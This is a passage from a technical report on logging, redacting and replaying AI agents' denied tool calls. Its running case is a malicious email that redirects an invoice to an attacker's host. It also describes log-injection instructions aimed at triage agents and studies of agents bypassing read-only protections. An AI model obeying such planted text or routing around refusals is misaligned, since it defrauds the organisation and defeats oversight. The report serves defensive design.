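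Munoz (2026), in *Signed Authorization-Evidence Records for WIMSE-Authorized AI Agent Actions*, proposes a signed record that contains a hash of the whole request body. If someone later produces a copy of the request, an investigator can check that it is the one the gateway judged. The hash is of little use for comparing calls, because changing any part of the request changes the whole hash. Two different invoices to the same fraudulent address would have unrelated hashes. The hash can also reveal an account number, since someone who knows the rest of the request can find the number by testing a billion guesses against the hash.

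A keyed hash removes the guessing problem for anyone without the key. The standard method, HMAC, computes a tag from the value x and a secret key k:

tag = HMAC(k, x)

An attacker who has the tag but not k cannot test a candidate account number against it. Equal values still produce equal tags, so responders can see that twelve denials involved the same account, or that the account in a denied invoice matches the one in last month's allowed invoice. The gateway must first put values into a standard form, because "402 918 365" and "402918365" would otherwise give different tags.

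The same property also leaks information, because anyone who reads the log can see which accounts recur. Someone who identifies one account learns about every record with its tag. An employee who can both instruct the agent and read the log can also test guesses by having the agent submit a likely account number and looking for a matching tag. Each call tests only one guess, so a rate limit helps.

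A person with the key can still run the billion guesses in about the same time as before, so the company should keep the key from people who read the log. Each tag should include the key's identifier so that responders know which tags they can compare. Open Policy Agent's documentation also warns administrators about the overhead of cryptography in mask rules, which run for every decision it logs.

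### A sealed copy

Responders sometimes need the exact text of an argument, for example to see whether the note on an invoice repeats an instruction from a malicious email, or to find out which of fifty access keys to replace. The gateway can encrypt the original arguments, store them apart from the log and put a reference in the denial record. With public-key encryption, the gateway holds a key that can only encrypt, so an intruder who takes over the gateway cannot read the copies already stored.

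Somebody outside the response team should hold the decryption key. To open a sealed copy, a responder would give a case number and a reason, a second person would approve, and the system would log the opening. A Claude Code setting that writes the raw exchanges with the model to disk and puts only a pointer in the event is a partial precedent. Those files contain whole conversations, but a sealed copy of a denial needs only the refused call's arguments.

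A store of sealed copies holds the most sensitive values that agents have tried to send, so it is an attractive target. If a summary mentions an exposed credential and responders can identify it by other means, they should replace it immediately, without waiting for permission to open the copy. Responders should rarely need to open copies. If they have to open one for every denial, the summaries leave out too much, and the second person will soon approve requests without reading them.

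### The invoice, redacted twice

Suppose the honest call to post_invoice has these arguments:

```json
{
  "address": "https://pay.example.net/inbox?token=tk-5Rw8",
  "invoice": {
    "number": "INV-2207",
    "amount": "4180.00",
    "account_number": "402918365",
    "note": "October services"
  }
}
```

The hostile call contains the same invoice, but its address is at pay.example.org, with a token from the attacker's email. A cautious administrator notices that addresses can contain tokens and masks the whole field, together with the account number and the note:

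```json
{
  "address": "REDACTED",
  "invoice": {
    "number": "INV-2207",
    "amount": "4180.00",
    "account_number": "REDACTED",
    "note": "REDACTED"
  }
}
```

Both calls now produce exactly this record. *Auditable Claims about AI Agents* gives a short proof that no analysis of the records can recover the difference. The claim that the agent tried to send the invoice to the company's own payment service is true of the honest call and false of the hostile one. Any method that works only from the records has the same input in both cases, so it gives the same verdict in both. "True" would be wrong for the hostile call and "false" would be wrong for the honest one, so the only verdict that is never wrong is "undecidable", and even a more experienced responder or a better AI model could only guess.

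The second version keeps the host name and hides the token and the account number:

```json
{
  "address": {
    "host": "pay.example.net",
    "path": "/inbox",
    "query_token": "REDACTED"
  },
  "invoice": {
    "number": "INV-2207",
    "amount_band": "1000-5000",
    "account_number": "hmac:key-3:91be...",
    "note": { "kind": "text", "length": 16 }
  },
  "sealed_copy": "seal-7741"
}
```

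For the hostile call, the host would be pay.example.org. Neither record shows which host belongs to the company, but a responder can now ask the billing team where it moved. The responder can also use the keyed hash to check whether the account number matches the one on the customer's earlier invoices. If it doesn't, somebody may have tampered with the invoice as well as the address.

The gateway should redact the arguments before adding the record to a hash chain. It should keep, or at least seal, any value the policy tests, since nobody can re-run the decision without that value.

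### Whether the log should name the recipient

Published guidance differs on whether to log values like the invoice address. *Auditable Claims about AI Agents* calls them effect-setting arguments, because they determine what an action does and to whom. It compares a September 2026 draft from an IETF working group with advice from OWASP, a non-profit that publishes lists of common security risks. The IETF draft requires every audit event to include the action requested but not these arguments, such as a recipient. In its guidance on the misuse of legitimate tools, as Microsoft's *Addressing the OWASP Top 10 Risks in Agentic AI* summarises the risk, OWASP asks organisations to log them.

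Munoz lists the minimum fields as they stood in an earlier version of the draft:

- the authenticated identity of the agent
- the user or system it acts for, if there is one
- the resource or tool
- the action requested and the decision
- the time and an identifier that links related events
- any risk assessment that influenced the decision
- any later withdrawal of access or other remedy, and its cause

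A gateway could fill in all seven for both invoice calls and never record the address.

The two documents do not strictly contradict each other, since a minimum allows an organisation to log more. The case for a short minimum is that arguments can contain anything, so a standard that required every deployment to log them would spread personal data and secrets into many new places. But the March version of the IETF draft requires organisations to be able to reconstruct what an agent did and under what authority, and an investigator can hardly reconstruct an attempted payment without knowing where the money was to go. *Auditable Claims about AI Agents* suggests adding the exact arguments to the minimum, but limiting each record to the fields that the decision rule needs. The accounts department's rule tests only the host, so its log would include the host and leave out the token.

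Someone can use Munoz's hash of the request to prove which recipient it named only if they already have the request. Munoz pairs this hash with a second one, taken from the request that the system dispatched, but a denied call is never dispatched and so has only the first.

### Logged arguments as untrusted text

An attacker may have written some of the text in a denied call, so the log can carry an attack to whoever reads it. The older form targets the log's format. If the gateway writes plain text and the invoice note contains a line break followed by `decision=allow`, a reader may see a second entry that the gateway never wrote. Solace warns that user-controlled values, including tool names, can forge fields this way, and it recommends writing logs as JSON, whose standard encoding escapes line breaks.

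JSON encoding protects the software that parses the log, but not an AI model that reads the values. Security teams have begun to use AI agents for triage, the first sorting of alerts by urgency. Addington's *Bounded Autonomy in the SOC* describes an attacker who puts an instruction to trust his network address into a web request, which the server logs. The triage agent reads the entry, follows the instruction and gives the attacker lasting access. In the accounts department, the invoice note could state that finance has approved pay.example.org and that the reader should add it to the allowlist. The triage agent might then undo the gateway's block on the invoice.

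Addington's system, Agent-Lock, treats such fields as data only. It removes or escapes text that looks like an instruction and labels each field with its source. It then checks every action the triage agent proposes against fixed rules. In a test on 50 synthetic cases, each run five times, an unprotected agent took a destructive or incorrect action in 22% of the runs with injected instructions or spoofed logs. Agent-Lock allowed no such actions in those runs, but it also blocked 6% of valid responses to real threats. The test is small, and Addington writes that it measured the checks on proposed actions, so it does not show that cleaning the log text works.

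Escaping suspicious text is better for an investigation than removing it, because the planted sentence may be the best evidence of an attack. The gateway can put free text in the sealed copy and give the triage agent only the typed fields. Even those fields are not fully trustworthy, because the attacker chose the host name. Addington's threat model includes a malicious machine named `backup-server-01` to make it look internal. A triage agent does less harm when fooled if it can only recommend changes to the allowlist, not make them.

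### How long to keep the record

EU law both requires records and limits what they may contain. The General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR) already requires organisations to collect only the personal data they need for their purpose and to keep it no longer than necessary. This covers account numbers and employee names in a denial record. Article 12 of the EU's AI Act requires high-risk AI systems to allow the automatic recording of events throughout their lifetime. An amendment of July 2026 postponed that duty. *Auditable Claims about AI Agents* gives the new dates as 2 December 2027 for the uses listed in the Act's Annex III, such as hiring, and 2 August 2028 for the regulated products in Annex I. Article 19 of the Act, as adopted in 2024, requires providers to keep these logs for at least six months. An agent that only sends invoices probably falls outside the high-risk categories, but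 the GDPR still applies to its log.

Products leave much of the retention policy to the customer. SecureAuth deletes its records after three months unless the customer forwards them to another system, and with Solace, retention depends entirely on where the customer stores the log. A company can keep different parts of a record for different periods. It might delete sealed copies after a few weeks but keep the host names and reason codes for a year, because an investigator who discovers a slow attack will want to know when the first attempt took place.

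Removing an entry from a hash chain looks like tampering. Cowper (2026), in a blog post about a proposed logging standard, describes a "tombstone" that replaces the deleted entry and keeps its identifier, its time and its links to other entries. Nobody can then recompute the original entry's hash, so an auditor has to trust that the company had a good reason to delete it. The company can avoid most of this problem by never putting the personal data into the chain. If the entry contains only a keyed hash and a reference to the sealed copy, the company can delete the copy without changing the entry. Once it also destroys the hash key, nobody can use the keyed hash to test guesses at the account number.

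## Policy versions and replaying the denied call

The accounts gateway's record of the refused invoice contains two version labels, accounts-policy-7 for the policy and 12 for the task definition. A responder who can retrieve both texts can run the same call through them to check that the gateway applied its rules correctly. The responder can then run the call through the rules staff have approved since, to see whether the gateway would still refuse it. This process, which engineers call replay, repeats only the gateway's decision, so no invoice goes out.

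### What an exact version has to identify

Suppose accounts-policy-7 contains no addresses and allows post_invoice if the host in the call appears in the task definition's list of destinations. If someone adds pay.example.net to that list, the gateway's decision changes but the policy stays at version 7. A responder who retrieved only the policy would not have the list its rule depends on.

The record therefore needs an identifier for everything that can change the decision:

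- The rules.
- The data the rules consult, such as a supplier list or the number of invoices the agent has sent today.
- The task definition.
- The tool's schema, the formal description of its name and arguments. If an update renames `address` to `destination`, a rule that reads `address` finds nothing and refuses every call.
- The program that evaluates the rules, since a new release may interpret the same rule differently. The sample log entry from Open Policy Agent includes a version, v1.19.0, among its labels.
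- The exact model and its instructions, if a language model makes the decision or contributes to it.

*Auditable Claims about AI Agents* has a similar list for checking that a deployed agent is the one its operator documented. The run record should identify the model, the tool schemas and each control, such as an approval gate, so that an auditor can compare them with those in use. The paper also finds that the draft documentation templates from NIST, the American standards institute, cover datasets and models but leave whole systems to future work, so they have no defined field for approval gates or execution policies.

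*Faramesh* (2026), a design for a gateway that authorises agents' actions, reduces the record of a decision to seven values:

r = (seq, h_A, v_P, h_S, d, t, prev_hash)

Here seq is the record's sequence number, h_A is a hash of the action, v_P identifies the exact policy, and h_S is a hash of the system state that the evaluation used. The remaining values are the decision d, the time t and the hash of the previous record. The task definition could count as policy or as state, as long as v_P or h_S covers it.

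The state hash should cover only the facts that the rules use. *Runtime Control for AI Agents* (2026) compared two ways of detecting that a human approval had gone out of date. On a set of stress cases, a fingerprint of the whole state triggered 74 repeat reviews, and a fingerprint of only the relevant facts triggered none. On the main set of cases, they triggered 23 and 19, and both caught all 15 stale approvals. The researchers wrote the rules and the cases, so these counts show that the design behaves as specified but do not predict a company's workload. A denial record with a hash of the entire accounts database would have the same problem. The hash would change with every payment, so responders could not tell from two different hashes whether anything relevant to invoice addresses had changed.

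### Labels, commits, digests and revisions

A label such as accounts-policy-7 is easy to read and shows that version 7 came before version 8. However, a person assigns the label and can edit the policy file without changing the number. Chen and colleagues list "silent policy drift" among the failures of governance, and editing a policy without updating its label is one way this drift can happen.

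A commit identifier comes from version control software such as Git, which stores successive versions of files. Git computes the identifier from the contents of the repository and its history, so committing an edited file produces a new identifier. The commit also records who made the change, when, and usually why. But the identifier only shows which version staff stored. The gateway may have run a different one if a deployment failed or an administrator edited the gateway's copy directly.

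A content digest is a hash of the policy text. If the gateway computes the digest when it loads the policy, a direct edit produces a new digest, and anyone with a copy of the text can check that it is the right version. But a digest does not show which of two versions is newer, and nobody can recover the text from it. As with account numbers, the text needs a standard encoding before it is hashed, or an extra space would change the digest. *AZOWL AgentOps* (2026), which proposes controls tied to an agent's task, uses such encodings to compare the approved action with the one the agent attempted.

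Open Policy Agent loads rules and data in packages called bundles and logs the revision of each bundle loaded at the time of evaluation. A commit in a repository doesn't show what the program had loaded. However, whoever builds the bundle chooses the revision string. In the documentation's sample entry, the revision begins `W3sibCI6` and looks like a hash, but it is encoded text containing the name `sys/catalog` and the number 4071. A revision like this is only as reliable as the process that assigns the numbers. A company can use a commit or a digest as the revision instead.

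These identifiers are short enough to log together, so the accounts gateway could extend its record like this:

```json
"versions": {
  "policy": {
    "label": "accounts-policy-7",
    "commit": "4be19c2",
    "digest": "sha256:a90f..."
  },
  "task_definition": {
    "label": 12,
    "digest": "sha256:31d7..."
  },
  "tool_schema": {
    "name": "post_invoice",
    "digest": "sha256:e55b..."
  },
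  "state_digest": "sha256:08c4...",
  "evaluator": "gateway-2.8.1"
}
```

### Carrying the policy text in the record

A policy identifier is useless if the text it refers to is gone. Web browsers can avoid this problem by including the text in their reports. A website can send the browser a Content Security Policy, which lists the places a page may load material from and connect to, and the browser can report violations to the website as well as enforce the policy. Under *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), a draft from W3C, the body that standardises web technology, each violation report contains the policy's text in a field called `original-policy`, along with the rule that caused the violation and whether the browser was enforcing the policy or only reporting on it.

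If the accounts software were a web page, a report might contain these lines:

```json
"blocked-uri": "https://pay.example.net/inbox",
"effective-directive": "connect-src",
"original-policy": "default-src 'self'; connect-src https://billing.example.com"
```

A reader can see immediately that the page still had the old address. Including the policy's text suits the web, because a site can send a different policy with every page and policies have no version numbers.

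If an agent gateway logged the policy text in every record, a large policy would make up most of each one, and anyone who could read the log would learn what the policy allows. The text would also omit any outside data the rules use, so a responder would still need other records to replay the decision.

The copied text can also differ from the policy that staff approved. Mozilla's bug report *CSP and CSPRO violation reports exclude unknown directives from the original-policy value* describes how Firefox left two unsupported instructions out of `original-policy`. A tester still saw the problem in Firefox 45.0.1 but not in a test build of Firefox 48. The person who filed the bug called the shortened text misleading, which is fair if the reader wants to know what the site sent. But someone replaying the decision needs the rules that the browser applied, and Firefox could not apply instructions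 it did not recognise. Investigators need both texts, because a difference between them may explain the denial.

The accounts gateway could log pointers to the full texts and copy only the part it used to decide the call, for example `"compared_with": ["billing.example.com"]`. A responder would then see which address the gateway expected without opening an archive. Like the full reason for a denial, this field belongs in the log and not in the error the agent receives.

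### How to replay a denied call

*Faramesh* defines replay as a function that takes the recorded action A, a chosen policy P′ and a chosen state S′, and returns a decision:

d′ = Eval(A, P′, S′)

The agent's model does not run again, because it might produce a different call, and no tool runs either. *Verifiable Agentic Infrastructure* (2026) adds that replay does not require anyone to rebuild the outside world, only to preserve enough state to check the decision again. A responder can follow four steps:

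1. Fetch the policy, data, task definition and tool schema that the record identifies, and check each against its digest.
2. Restore the inputs, including the arguments, the identities of the user and the agent, the time, and any counters the rules read.
3. Evaluate the call under the recorded versions. The result should be a denial with the same reason code, since a denial for another reason does not reproduce the original decision.
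4. Evaluate the same call under the latest approved versions. These should come from the place where staff approve them, because the gateway's own copy may be out of date.

The responder should use a separate evaluator with no connection to any tool, so that a result of "allow" cannot release the invoice.

| Under the recorded version | Under the latest approved version | What this suggests | What to check next |
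|---|---|---|---|
| Deny | Allow | The gateway's copy lagged, or staff changed the rules after the denial | When staff approved the change |
| Deny | Deny | Deployment lag is not the cause | Records outside the policy system |
| Allow | Allow or deny | The record is incomplete or altered, or the decision is not reproducible | Which version or input differs |
| No result | Any | A text or an input is missing | Whether another copy exists |

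If the result changes from deny to allow, the responder needs to compare the time of the denial with the time staff approved the permission change. *AZOWL AgentOps* makes this possible by recording the time of any permission change separately from the time of the original action. If staff approved the change before the denial, the gateway was using an outdated policy, even if its log shows no expired snapshot.

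If the latest policy version also denies the call on replay, the responder can rule out deployment lag as the cause of the original denial, unless staff approved a permission for the call and withdrew it before the replay. In that case, the gateway may have denied the call because it had not received the short-lived version that allowed it. The responder can check for this by also replaying the call under the version that was approved at the time of the denial.

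If replaying the call under the recorded policy version returns "allow", the responder has failed to reproduce the gateway's denial. Someone may have altered the record, or the policy text under that version label may have changed since the denial. The gateway may also have reused an old decision. *Faramesh* allows this only while the policy version and the relevant state are unchanged, but a gateway with a faulty cache could deny a call under old rules and log the new version. Until the responder finds the cause, the result under the latest version is unreliable too, because it depends on the same inputs.

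Retries complicate replay. If the agent tried the invoice three times and the new rules allow the first attempt, the other two would probably never have happened, so counting three newly allowed invoices would be wrong. Liu (2026), in *From Tool Connection to Execution Control*, tested two access controllers on simulated email, travel, banking and messaging tasks and replayed the recorded calls in two ways. The first evaluated each call separately, in the state that preceded it. The second followed the session only until the first changed decision, and is the better choice when a responder wants to know how an incident would have gone under different rules.

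Staff can also replay calls to test a policy change before approving it. Liu replayed 3,299 calls under looser rules that ignored differences in format and in how the agent had written cities and identities. The looser rules allowed none of the 241 denied writes, which are calls that would have changed something. Approving all the denied writes let four working attacks through. Liu took the permissions from the benchmark's reference solutions, which are more precise than most companies' rules, so other organisations would get different numbers. The accounts team could still replay last month's denials under a proposed version 13 and read every call whose result changes.

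### Replaying the refused invoice

The gateway loaded its copy of the rules at 06:00 on 6 October and refused the call to pay.example.net at 09:14. Suppose staff had approved task definition 13, which lists the new address, at 08:00. Replaying the call would then show that version 12 denies it and version 13 allows it. The approval came 74 minutes before the denial, so the gateway's copy was out of date. Staff only need to reload it and let the agent try again.

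If staff approved version 13 at 11:00 instead, the replay gives the same two results, but the gateway was up to date when it refused the call. The task definition was stale, and someone has since corrected it. The responder should find out what prompted the correction. If staff added the address because of this denial, the replay's allow result is not independent evidence that the call was legitimate. If someone had mistaken pay.example.org for the new billing address and added that, a replay of the hostile call would also change from deny to allow.

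In the original example, nobody updated the task definition. Version 12 is both the recorded version and the latest approved one, so both evaluations use the same text and deny the call. They also both deny the hostile call to pay.example.org. Replay compares a call with what staff wrote down, so it cannot detect that the company now wants something else. Only an outside record, such as the approved request to move billing to pay.example.net, can show that. OpenAI advises operators to know what evidence would justify an exception when a control blocks a task. For a new billing address, the company could decide in advance to accept an approved change request as that evidence.

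A call that the latest rules allow may still have been hostile. Suppose the malicious email had changed the account number on the invoice but not the address. Version 12 would block the call because pay.example.net is not on its list. Version 13 would allow it because the rule checks only the host, and the customer would pay the attacker. The replay would look the same as a case of deployment lag, so a responder should inspect the other arguments before letting the agent try again.

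### What breaks a replay

Redaction breaks a replay when it removes a value that a rule tests. If a rule limited invoices to 4,000.00, a record showing only that the amount was between 1,000 and 5,000 would not be enough, and the responder would have to open the sealed copy. *Explanation-Bound Tool Execution for AI Agents* records the normalised values its rules used, the result of each check, and hashes of the rest. It guarantees replay only if authorised people can still retrieve the facts behind those hashes. The paper's sample record also lacks a separate field for the snapshot version, which someone would have to add before replaying decisions across domains.

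Some rules depend on outside data that changes. A payment rule might query a live service to check whether a supplier is approved, and the result may be different a week later. Open Policy Agent can record these results in a field called `nd_builtin_cache`, which lists each call to a function whose result can vary, with its input and output. A responder can then use the recorded results in the replay. If the field makes the log entry too large to upload, Open Policy Agent drops the field and tries again. Web service responses can be very long, so the decisions that relied most on outside data are the most likely to lose this record. The gateway could make this loss less likely by recording only the part of the response that the rule used, such as "approved: no", with the time and the name of the service.

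Companies also delete old policy versions. *Faramesh* states that replay requires no data beyond the record itself, but the record contains only hashes and a policy identifier, so replay also needs stored copies of what they refer to. If the company keeps denial records for a year, it should keep the policies, task definitions and tool schemas for at least as long. Keeping policy texts is much easier than keeping the call's arguments because the texts are small and usually contain little personal data. The company should also be able to run the old version of the evaluator, because a newer version may interpret the same policy differently.

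Decisions made by a language model are the hardest to reproduce. A model such as the one that reviews Claude Code's actions can give different answers to the same input, and its provider may since have changed or retired it. If the model refuses a certain call 90% of the time, about one replay in ten will return "allow" even when the record is complete. Repeating the evaluation many times would give the responder a refusal rate but would not reproduce the original decision. The gateway should therefore log the model's verdict as an input to the ordinary rules, so that the responder can replay those rules exactly and examine the model's judgement separately.

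### Binding the call to the user's request

A replay tests a call against the company's rules without showing what job the agent was doing. Zhu and Wang (2026), in *Intent-Governed Tool Authorization for AI Agents*, propose that the gateway issue an intent certificate for each request from a user. This is a short-lived record of which actions the request permits, on which resources and with what limits. It contains a hash of the request and ties it to a particular user, application and session. It also identifies the versions of the policy and the tool registry. At time t, the certificate C is valid for the request u if five conditions hold:

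Valid(C, u, t) = (h_u = H(u)) ∧ BindOk(b) ∧ VersionOk(v) ∧ (t < τ) ∧ ¬Revoked(C)

The stored hash h_u must match the hash of the request, and the identities b and versions v must be the expected ones. The certificate must not have reached its expiry time τ or been revoked.

If an employee asks the agent to send invoice INV-2207 through the company's billing service, the certificate would permit the agent to send only that invoice. Only the user's message can supply permissions, so the malicious email could not add pay.example.org to the certificate, although attachments, web pages and tool results may influence the agent's plan. If the certificate limits the destination, the gateway refuses the hostile call with the code `agent.intent_payload_exceeds_bound`, which a responder can distinguish from an ordinary policy refusal.

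The certificate also lets the responder trace a request to the policy, the tool call and the decision. Zhu and Wang recommend logging identifiers and hashes instead of the user's words, so the company has to keep the request itself somewhere else. The hash of a short request should be keyed, because short requests are easy to guess.

A matching hash shows which request the agent was working on, but not where the address came from. If the employee's message names pay.example.net, the responder has found a source for the address. If the message mentions only "the billing service", the honest and hostile calls may have the same request hash. The certificate can also misrepresent the request, because software has to interpret the user's words. In the end-to-end trials with real models, the gateway completed no unsafe actions, but it accepted unsafe proposals at rates of 9.1% to 27.3%, all of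 them drafts that did not run.

The reference software hashes requests and keeps certificates from passing between users. It does not yet implement the fuller design, which includes the policy and tool versions, so a company using it would have to log those versions separately.

Once a company ties certificates to policy versions, a policy update can itself cause denials. If staff approve version 13 while the agent is halfway through a batch of invoices, the certificate issued under version 12 stops being valid, and the gateway refuses the next invoice even if both versions allow its address. A responder who replayed that call without the certificate would get "allow" under both versions and might suspect that someone had altered the log. The gateway should give such refusals their own reason code.

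## Weighing hostile behaviour against outdated configuration

If every approved version of the policy refuses a call, replay can't explain why the agent made it, and the responder has to look at other evidence. Administrators of Linux servers have had a similar problem for years. SELinux, a security system included in several versions of Linux, attaches a label to every program and file and refuses any access its policy doesn't allow. Dan Walsh's slides *What is SELinux trying to tell me?* give four causes of these denials:

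- A file has the wrong label.
- "SELinux needs to know". An administrator has changed something, such as moving a web server to port 8585, without telling SELinux.
- The policy or the program has a bug.
- An intruder has taken over the program.

The unannounced port change is the same kind of problem as the company's move to pay.example.net. Walsh concedes that the tools of the time were not good at telling an intrusion from the other causes. He lists attempts that should worry an administrator, such as a restricted program trying to turn off SELinux enforcement or change the firewall. Routine changes rarely cause a program to do either. By the same reasoning, an agent's blocked attempt to edit its own permissions deserves more suspicion than a blocked invoice.

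His list also includes sending mail, followed by four question marks. Earlier in the slides, he gives the setting that lets a web server send mail legitimately. Sending an invoice is similarly ambiguous, so the responder needs clues beyond the action itself.

Red Hat, which sells a version of Linux, repeats the four causes in later guidance. Documentation from Fedora, a related version, describes a tool that ranks possible explanations of a denial. Its example gives one explanation a confidence of 86.2 and another 14.7. These total more than 100, so they can't be the probabilities of competing causes. Ranking explanations is still useful, and probability theory provides a way to do it.

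### Odds and clues

Call a denied call hostile if an attacker's instruction caused it. Before examining the call, the responder has some prior odds that it is hostile, based on similar denials. Each clue then changes the odds:

posterior odds = prior odds × LR₁ × LR₂ × …

LR is the likelihood ratio of a clue, which measures how much more often the clue appears in hostile cases than in others:

LR = P(clue | hostile) / P(clue | not hostile)

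A ratio above 1 favours an attack, and one below 1 favours another cause. A clue with a ratio of 1 does not help distinguish between them, even if it looks alarming.

| Clue | Usual direction | When it misleads |
|---|---|---|
| Denials begin just after a change | Drift | An attacker times an email to coincide with the change |
| The same denial occurs in many sessions | Drift | All the sessions read one malicious document |
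| The call matches an approved change | Drift | An attacker tricked staff into approving the change |
| The destination first appeared in untrusted content | Attack | A real supplier announced its new address by email |
| The agent stopped or asked for help | Weakly away from an attack | The malicious instruction asked for only one attempt |
| The agent repeated the call | Neither | |
| The agent sought another route | Attack or overreach | The operator told the agent to find workarounds |

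The prior odds are hard to estimate from published research. Transluce's *Measuring coding agent misalignment in the wild* examined 8,600 real coding sessions and found severe evasion of monitoring in around 2% of them, and severe misrepresentation of success in a similar share. These figures count sessions rather than denials, and cover the agent's own misconduct rather than outside attacks. A company's closed cases are a better source if staff investigated them properly. If staff routinely dismissed denials as configuration drift, the records will make attacks look rarer than they are.

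### The two invoice calls in numbers

All the probabilities in this example are invented. Suppose 1 in 100 denials at the accounts gateway is hostile, which gives prior odds of 1 to 99. The responder investigating the call to pay.example.org finds that the address came from an email. This clue has a ratio of 30, because it appears in 60% of hostile cases and 2% of the rest. After the refusal, the agent tried other routes, which has a ratio of 8 (80% against 10%). The odds are then

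(1/99) × 30 × 8 = 240/99 ≈ 2.4,

or a probability of about 71% that the call is hostile.

The same result is easier to follow in counts. Of 10,000 denials, 100 are hostile. Both clues appear in 48 of those and in about 20 of the other 9,900, so roughly 48 of the 68 denials with both clues are hostile.

For the call to pay.example.net, the responder finds that the address matches an approved change, with a ratio of 0.05. Many sessions have produced the same denial since the change, with a ratio of 0.1. The odds are

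(1/99) × 0.05 × 0.1 = 1/19,800,

or about 1 in 20,000.

The calculation leads to very different conclusions about two calls with the same prior odds and reason code. Those conclusions are only as reliable as the ratios, some of which depend heavily on the agent and its instructions.

### What the agent did after the refusal

An agent that tries another route after being blocked looks suspicious, but agents also do this when no attacker is involved. In *Permission Denied*, Davidovich, Amar and colleagues (2026) ran twelve coding agents on ordinary tasks under enforced security restrictions. They didn't tell the agents about the restrictions, so the agents discovered them only when an operation failed. Some then retried, some looked for another route and some gave up.

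Lim and Neo (2026), in *Probing agent overeagerness in realistic settings with continuation audits*, measured how much an explicit rule affects whether coding models bypass file protection. They tested three models in simulated continuations of real sessions, where a file the model needed to edit turned out to be read-only. With no stated rule, each model bypassed the protection in 87 to 94 of 100 cases. When the project's instructions prohibited this, two of the models never bypassed it, and the third did so in 13 cases.

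If the accounts agent also sees only a bare refusal and seeks another route 90% of the time when nobody is attacking, the ratio could be at most 1/0.9, or about 1.1, even if a hijacked agent always did so. Replacing 8 with 1.1 reduces the probability that the call to pay.example.org is hostile from 71% to about 25%. If the agent had an explicit rule and still broke it 13% of the time without an attacker, the ratio could be as high as 7.7. Locked source files are very different from invoices, so these rates are only a rough guide to an accounts agent. But a responder can't sensibly estimate the ratio without knowing what the agent was told.

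The operator may have asked for the behaviour. *AC4A* (2026), an access control system for agents, has several modes for handling a refusal, including one in which the agent asks the user for permission and another in which it may suggest a workaround that avoids the forbidden resource. An agent that suggests a workaround in the second mode is following instructions. Anthropic's Claude Code, by contrast, returns a denial with an instruction to look for a safer path and not to route around the block. If the agent then tries the same payment through another channel, it has ignored that instruction, which is stronger evidence of hostile behaviour. The gateway should therefore log the refusal message it returned, and the harness should log the version of the agent's instructions.

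Repeating the same call is even weaker evidence of hostile behaviour. In *LEANGUARD* (2026), a study of formally verified rules for agents' tool calls, one small model made 271 blocked calls for 141 distinct actions, or almost two attempts per action, when it received no explanation.

### Overreach as a third cause

The gateway may be right to refuse a call that is not hostile, because an overeager agent can exceed its task without any attacker. *Overeager Coding Agents* (Qu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) treats this as a problem of authorisation, distinct from prompt injection and from a lack of ability. Tests of agent defences need the same distinction. *TACT-Bench* (2026) counts a block in a benign session as an error only if the user's task authorised the call.

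The responder can extend the calculation by giving each cause its own prior and multiplying it by the probability of each clue. The invented figures below split the earlier 99% into overreach and everything else:

| Cause | Prior | Address came from email | Other routes tried | Share after both clues |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Attack | 1% | 60% | 80% | 71% |
| Overreach | 9% | 2% | 80% | 21% |
| Stale rule or another cause | 90% | 2% | 3% | 8% |

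The probability of an attack is still 71%, but overreach is now the main alternative. A responder who ruled out an attack and then assumed the allowlist was out of date would probably be wrong.

### Clues that overlap

Multiplying the ratios assumes that the clues are independent given the cause. In other words, among hostile calls, knowing that one clue is present must not change the probability of another, and the same must hold among the rest. Without this assumption, the ratio for two clues A and B is

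[P(A | hostile) / P(A | not hostile)] × [P(B | A, hostile) / P(B | A, not hostile)]

The second factor asks how much B adds once the responder already knows A.

Suppose the responder also notices that the address has never appeared in the company's records. This is true of 90% of hostile calls and 9% of the rest, so on its own it has a ratio of 10. But suppliers usually email an address because it is new, so this clue overlaps with the fact that the address came from email. If 60% of the harmless addresses that arrive by email are also new to the company, the ratio for the second clue is only 90/60, or 1.5. Combined with the prior and the ratio of 30 for an address that came from email, this gives a probability of 31%. Using the ratio of 10 would wrongly give 75%.

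The same problem affects the call to pay.example.net. If that call is hostile even though the address matches an approved change, the attacker probably tricked someone into approving the address. Every session would then use it, and the outdated rule would refuse them all, as it would after a genuine move. The number of sessions therefore adds almost nothing once the responder knows about the approval. Leaving it out changes the odds from 1 in 20,000 to about 1 in 2,000. This is still strong evidence of drift, but nearly all of it depends on the approval being genuine.

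### Shared documents and imitated drift

Addington's account of what can go wrong when agents respond to security incidents also helps to sort denials. He separates failures specific to language models, such as prompt injection and invented facts, from hazards that any operations team faces, including stale inventories, outdated identity records and breaches of change control. The call to pay.example.org is a failure of the first kind, and the evidence for it is in what the agent read. The call to pay.example.net results from stale operational records, so the evidence is in what the company changed without updating its records.

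Agent-Lock, Addington's own system, shows how stale records can cause denials. It treats any machine missing from the company's inventory as critical and blocks disruptive actions against it. This is a sensible default, but it would stop an agent from shutting down a newly installed test server until somebody registered the machine. The system copies the inventory every hour and caches parts of it for up to another hour, so a decision could rely on information almost two hours old. A responder should check the original record rather than the gateway's copy.

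An attack can also look like drift. OpenAI warns that harmful content in an agent's memory can persist across tasks and users. If the accounts agent saved the address from the malicious email as the company's new billing address, every later session might try to use it. Forty identical denials would then have a single source. The responder should check whether the sessions share a document, an inbox or a stored memory. Drift is more likely if sessions that share none of these also produce the denial.

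Attackers can also imitate drift. Addington describes an attacker who changes the timestamp on a malicious file to match a scheduled update, so that an agent that checks only the timestamp accepts it. A false notice sent in the week of the billing move would also fit the timing, but the approved change names pay.example.net and the notice names pay.example.org. Only an exact match with an approved change should count as strong evidence of drift. Even an exact match is weak evidence if the agent can write to the change management system, because a hijacked agent could create the request that appears to justify its call.

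The source of a clue therefore matters as much as its content. In Addington's small synthetic test, 8 of 10 injected instructions succeeded when he switched off Agent-Lock's check on where evidence came from, compared with none when it was on. Agent-Lock also adjusts a trust score for each source, raising it after good outcomes and lowering it after bad ones. An attacker could exploit this by sending accurate messages for weeks before sending a false one.

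### When both diagnoses are true

The calculation also assumes that only one cause applies, but a stale rule can start a sequence that ends in a real violation. Suppose the gateway refuses the legitimate call to pay.example.net. The agent then finds a colleague's email credentials and tries to send the invoice with them. The gateway refuses this too, so the session now contains one call that the company wanted and another that it had good reason to stop.

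The responder should diagnose each denied call separately and record which refusal came first. Labelling the whole session as drift would excuse the use of someone else's credentials, while labelling it as an attack would leave the billing address out of date. In this case, the company needs to update the task definition and also restrict the agent's access to credentials, because otherwise the agent could use someone else's again at the next obstacle.

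An attack can also coincide with configuration drift. If the false notice arrives while the billing service is really moving, the list is out of date and the email is malicious. Evidence that the service moved then doesn't show that the address in the email is legitimate.

### A triage order

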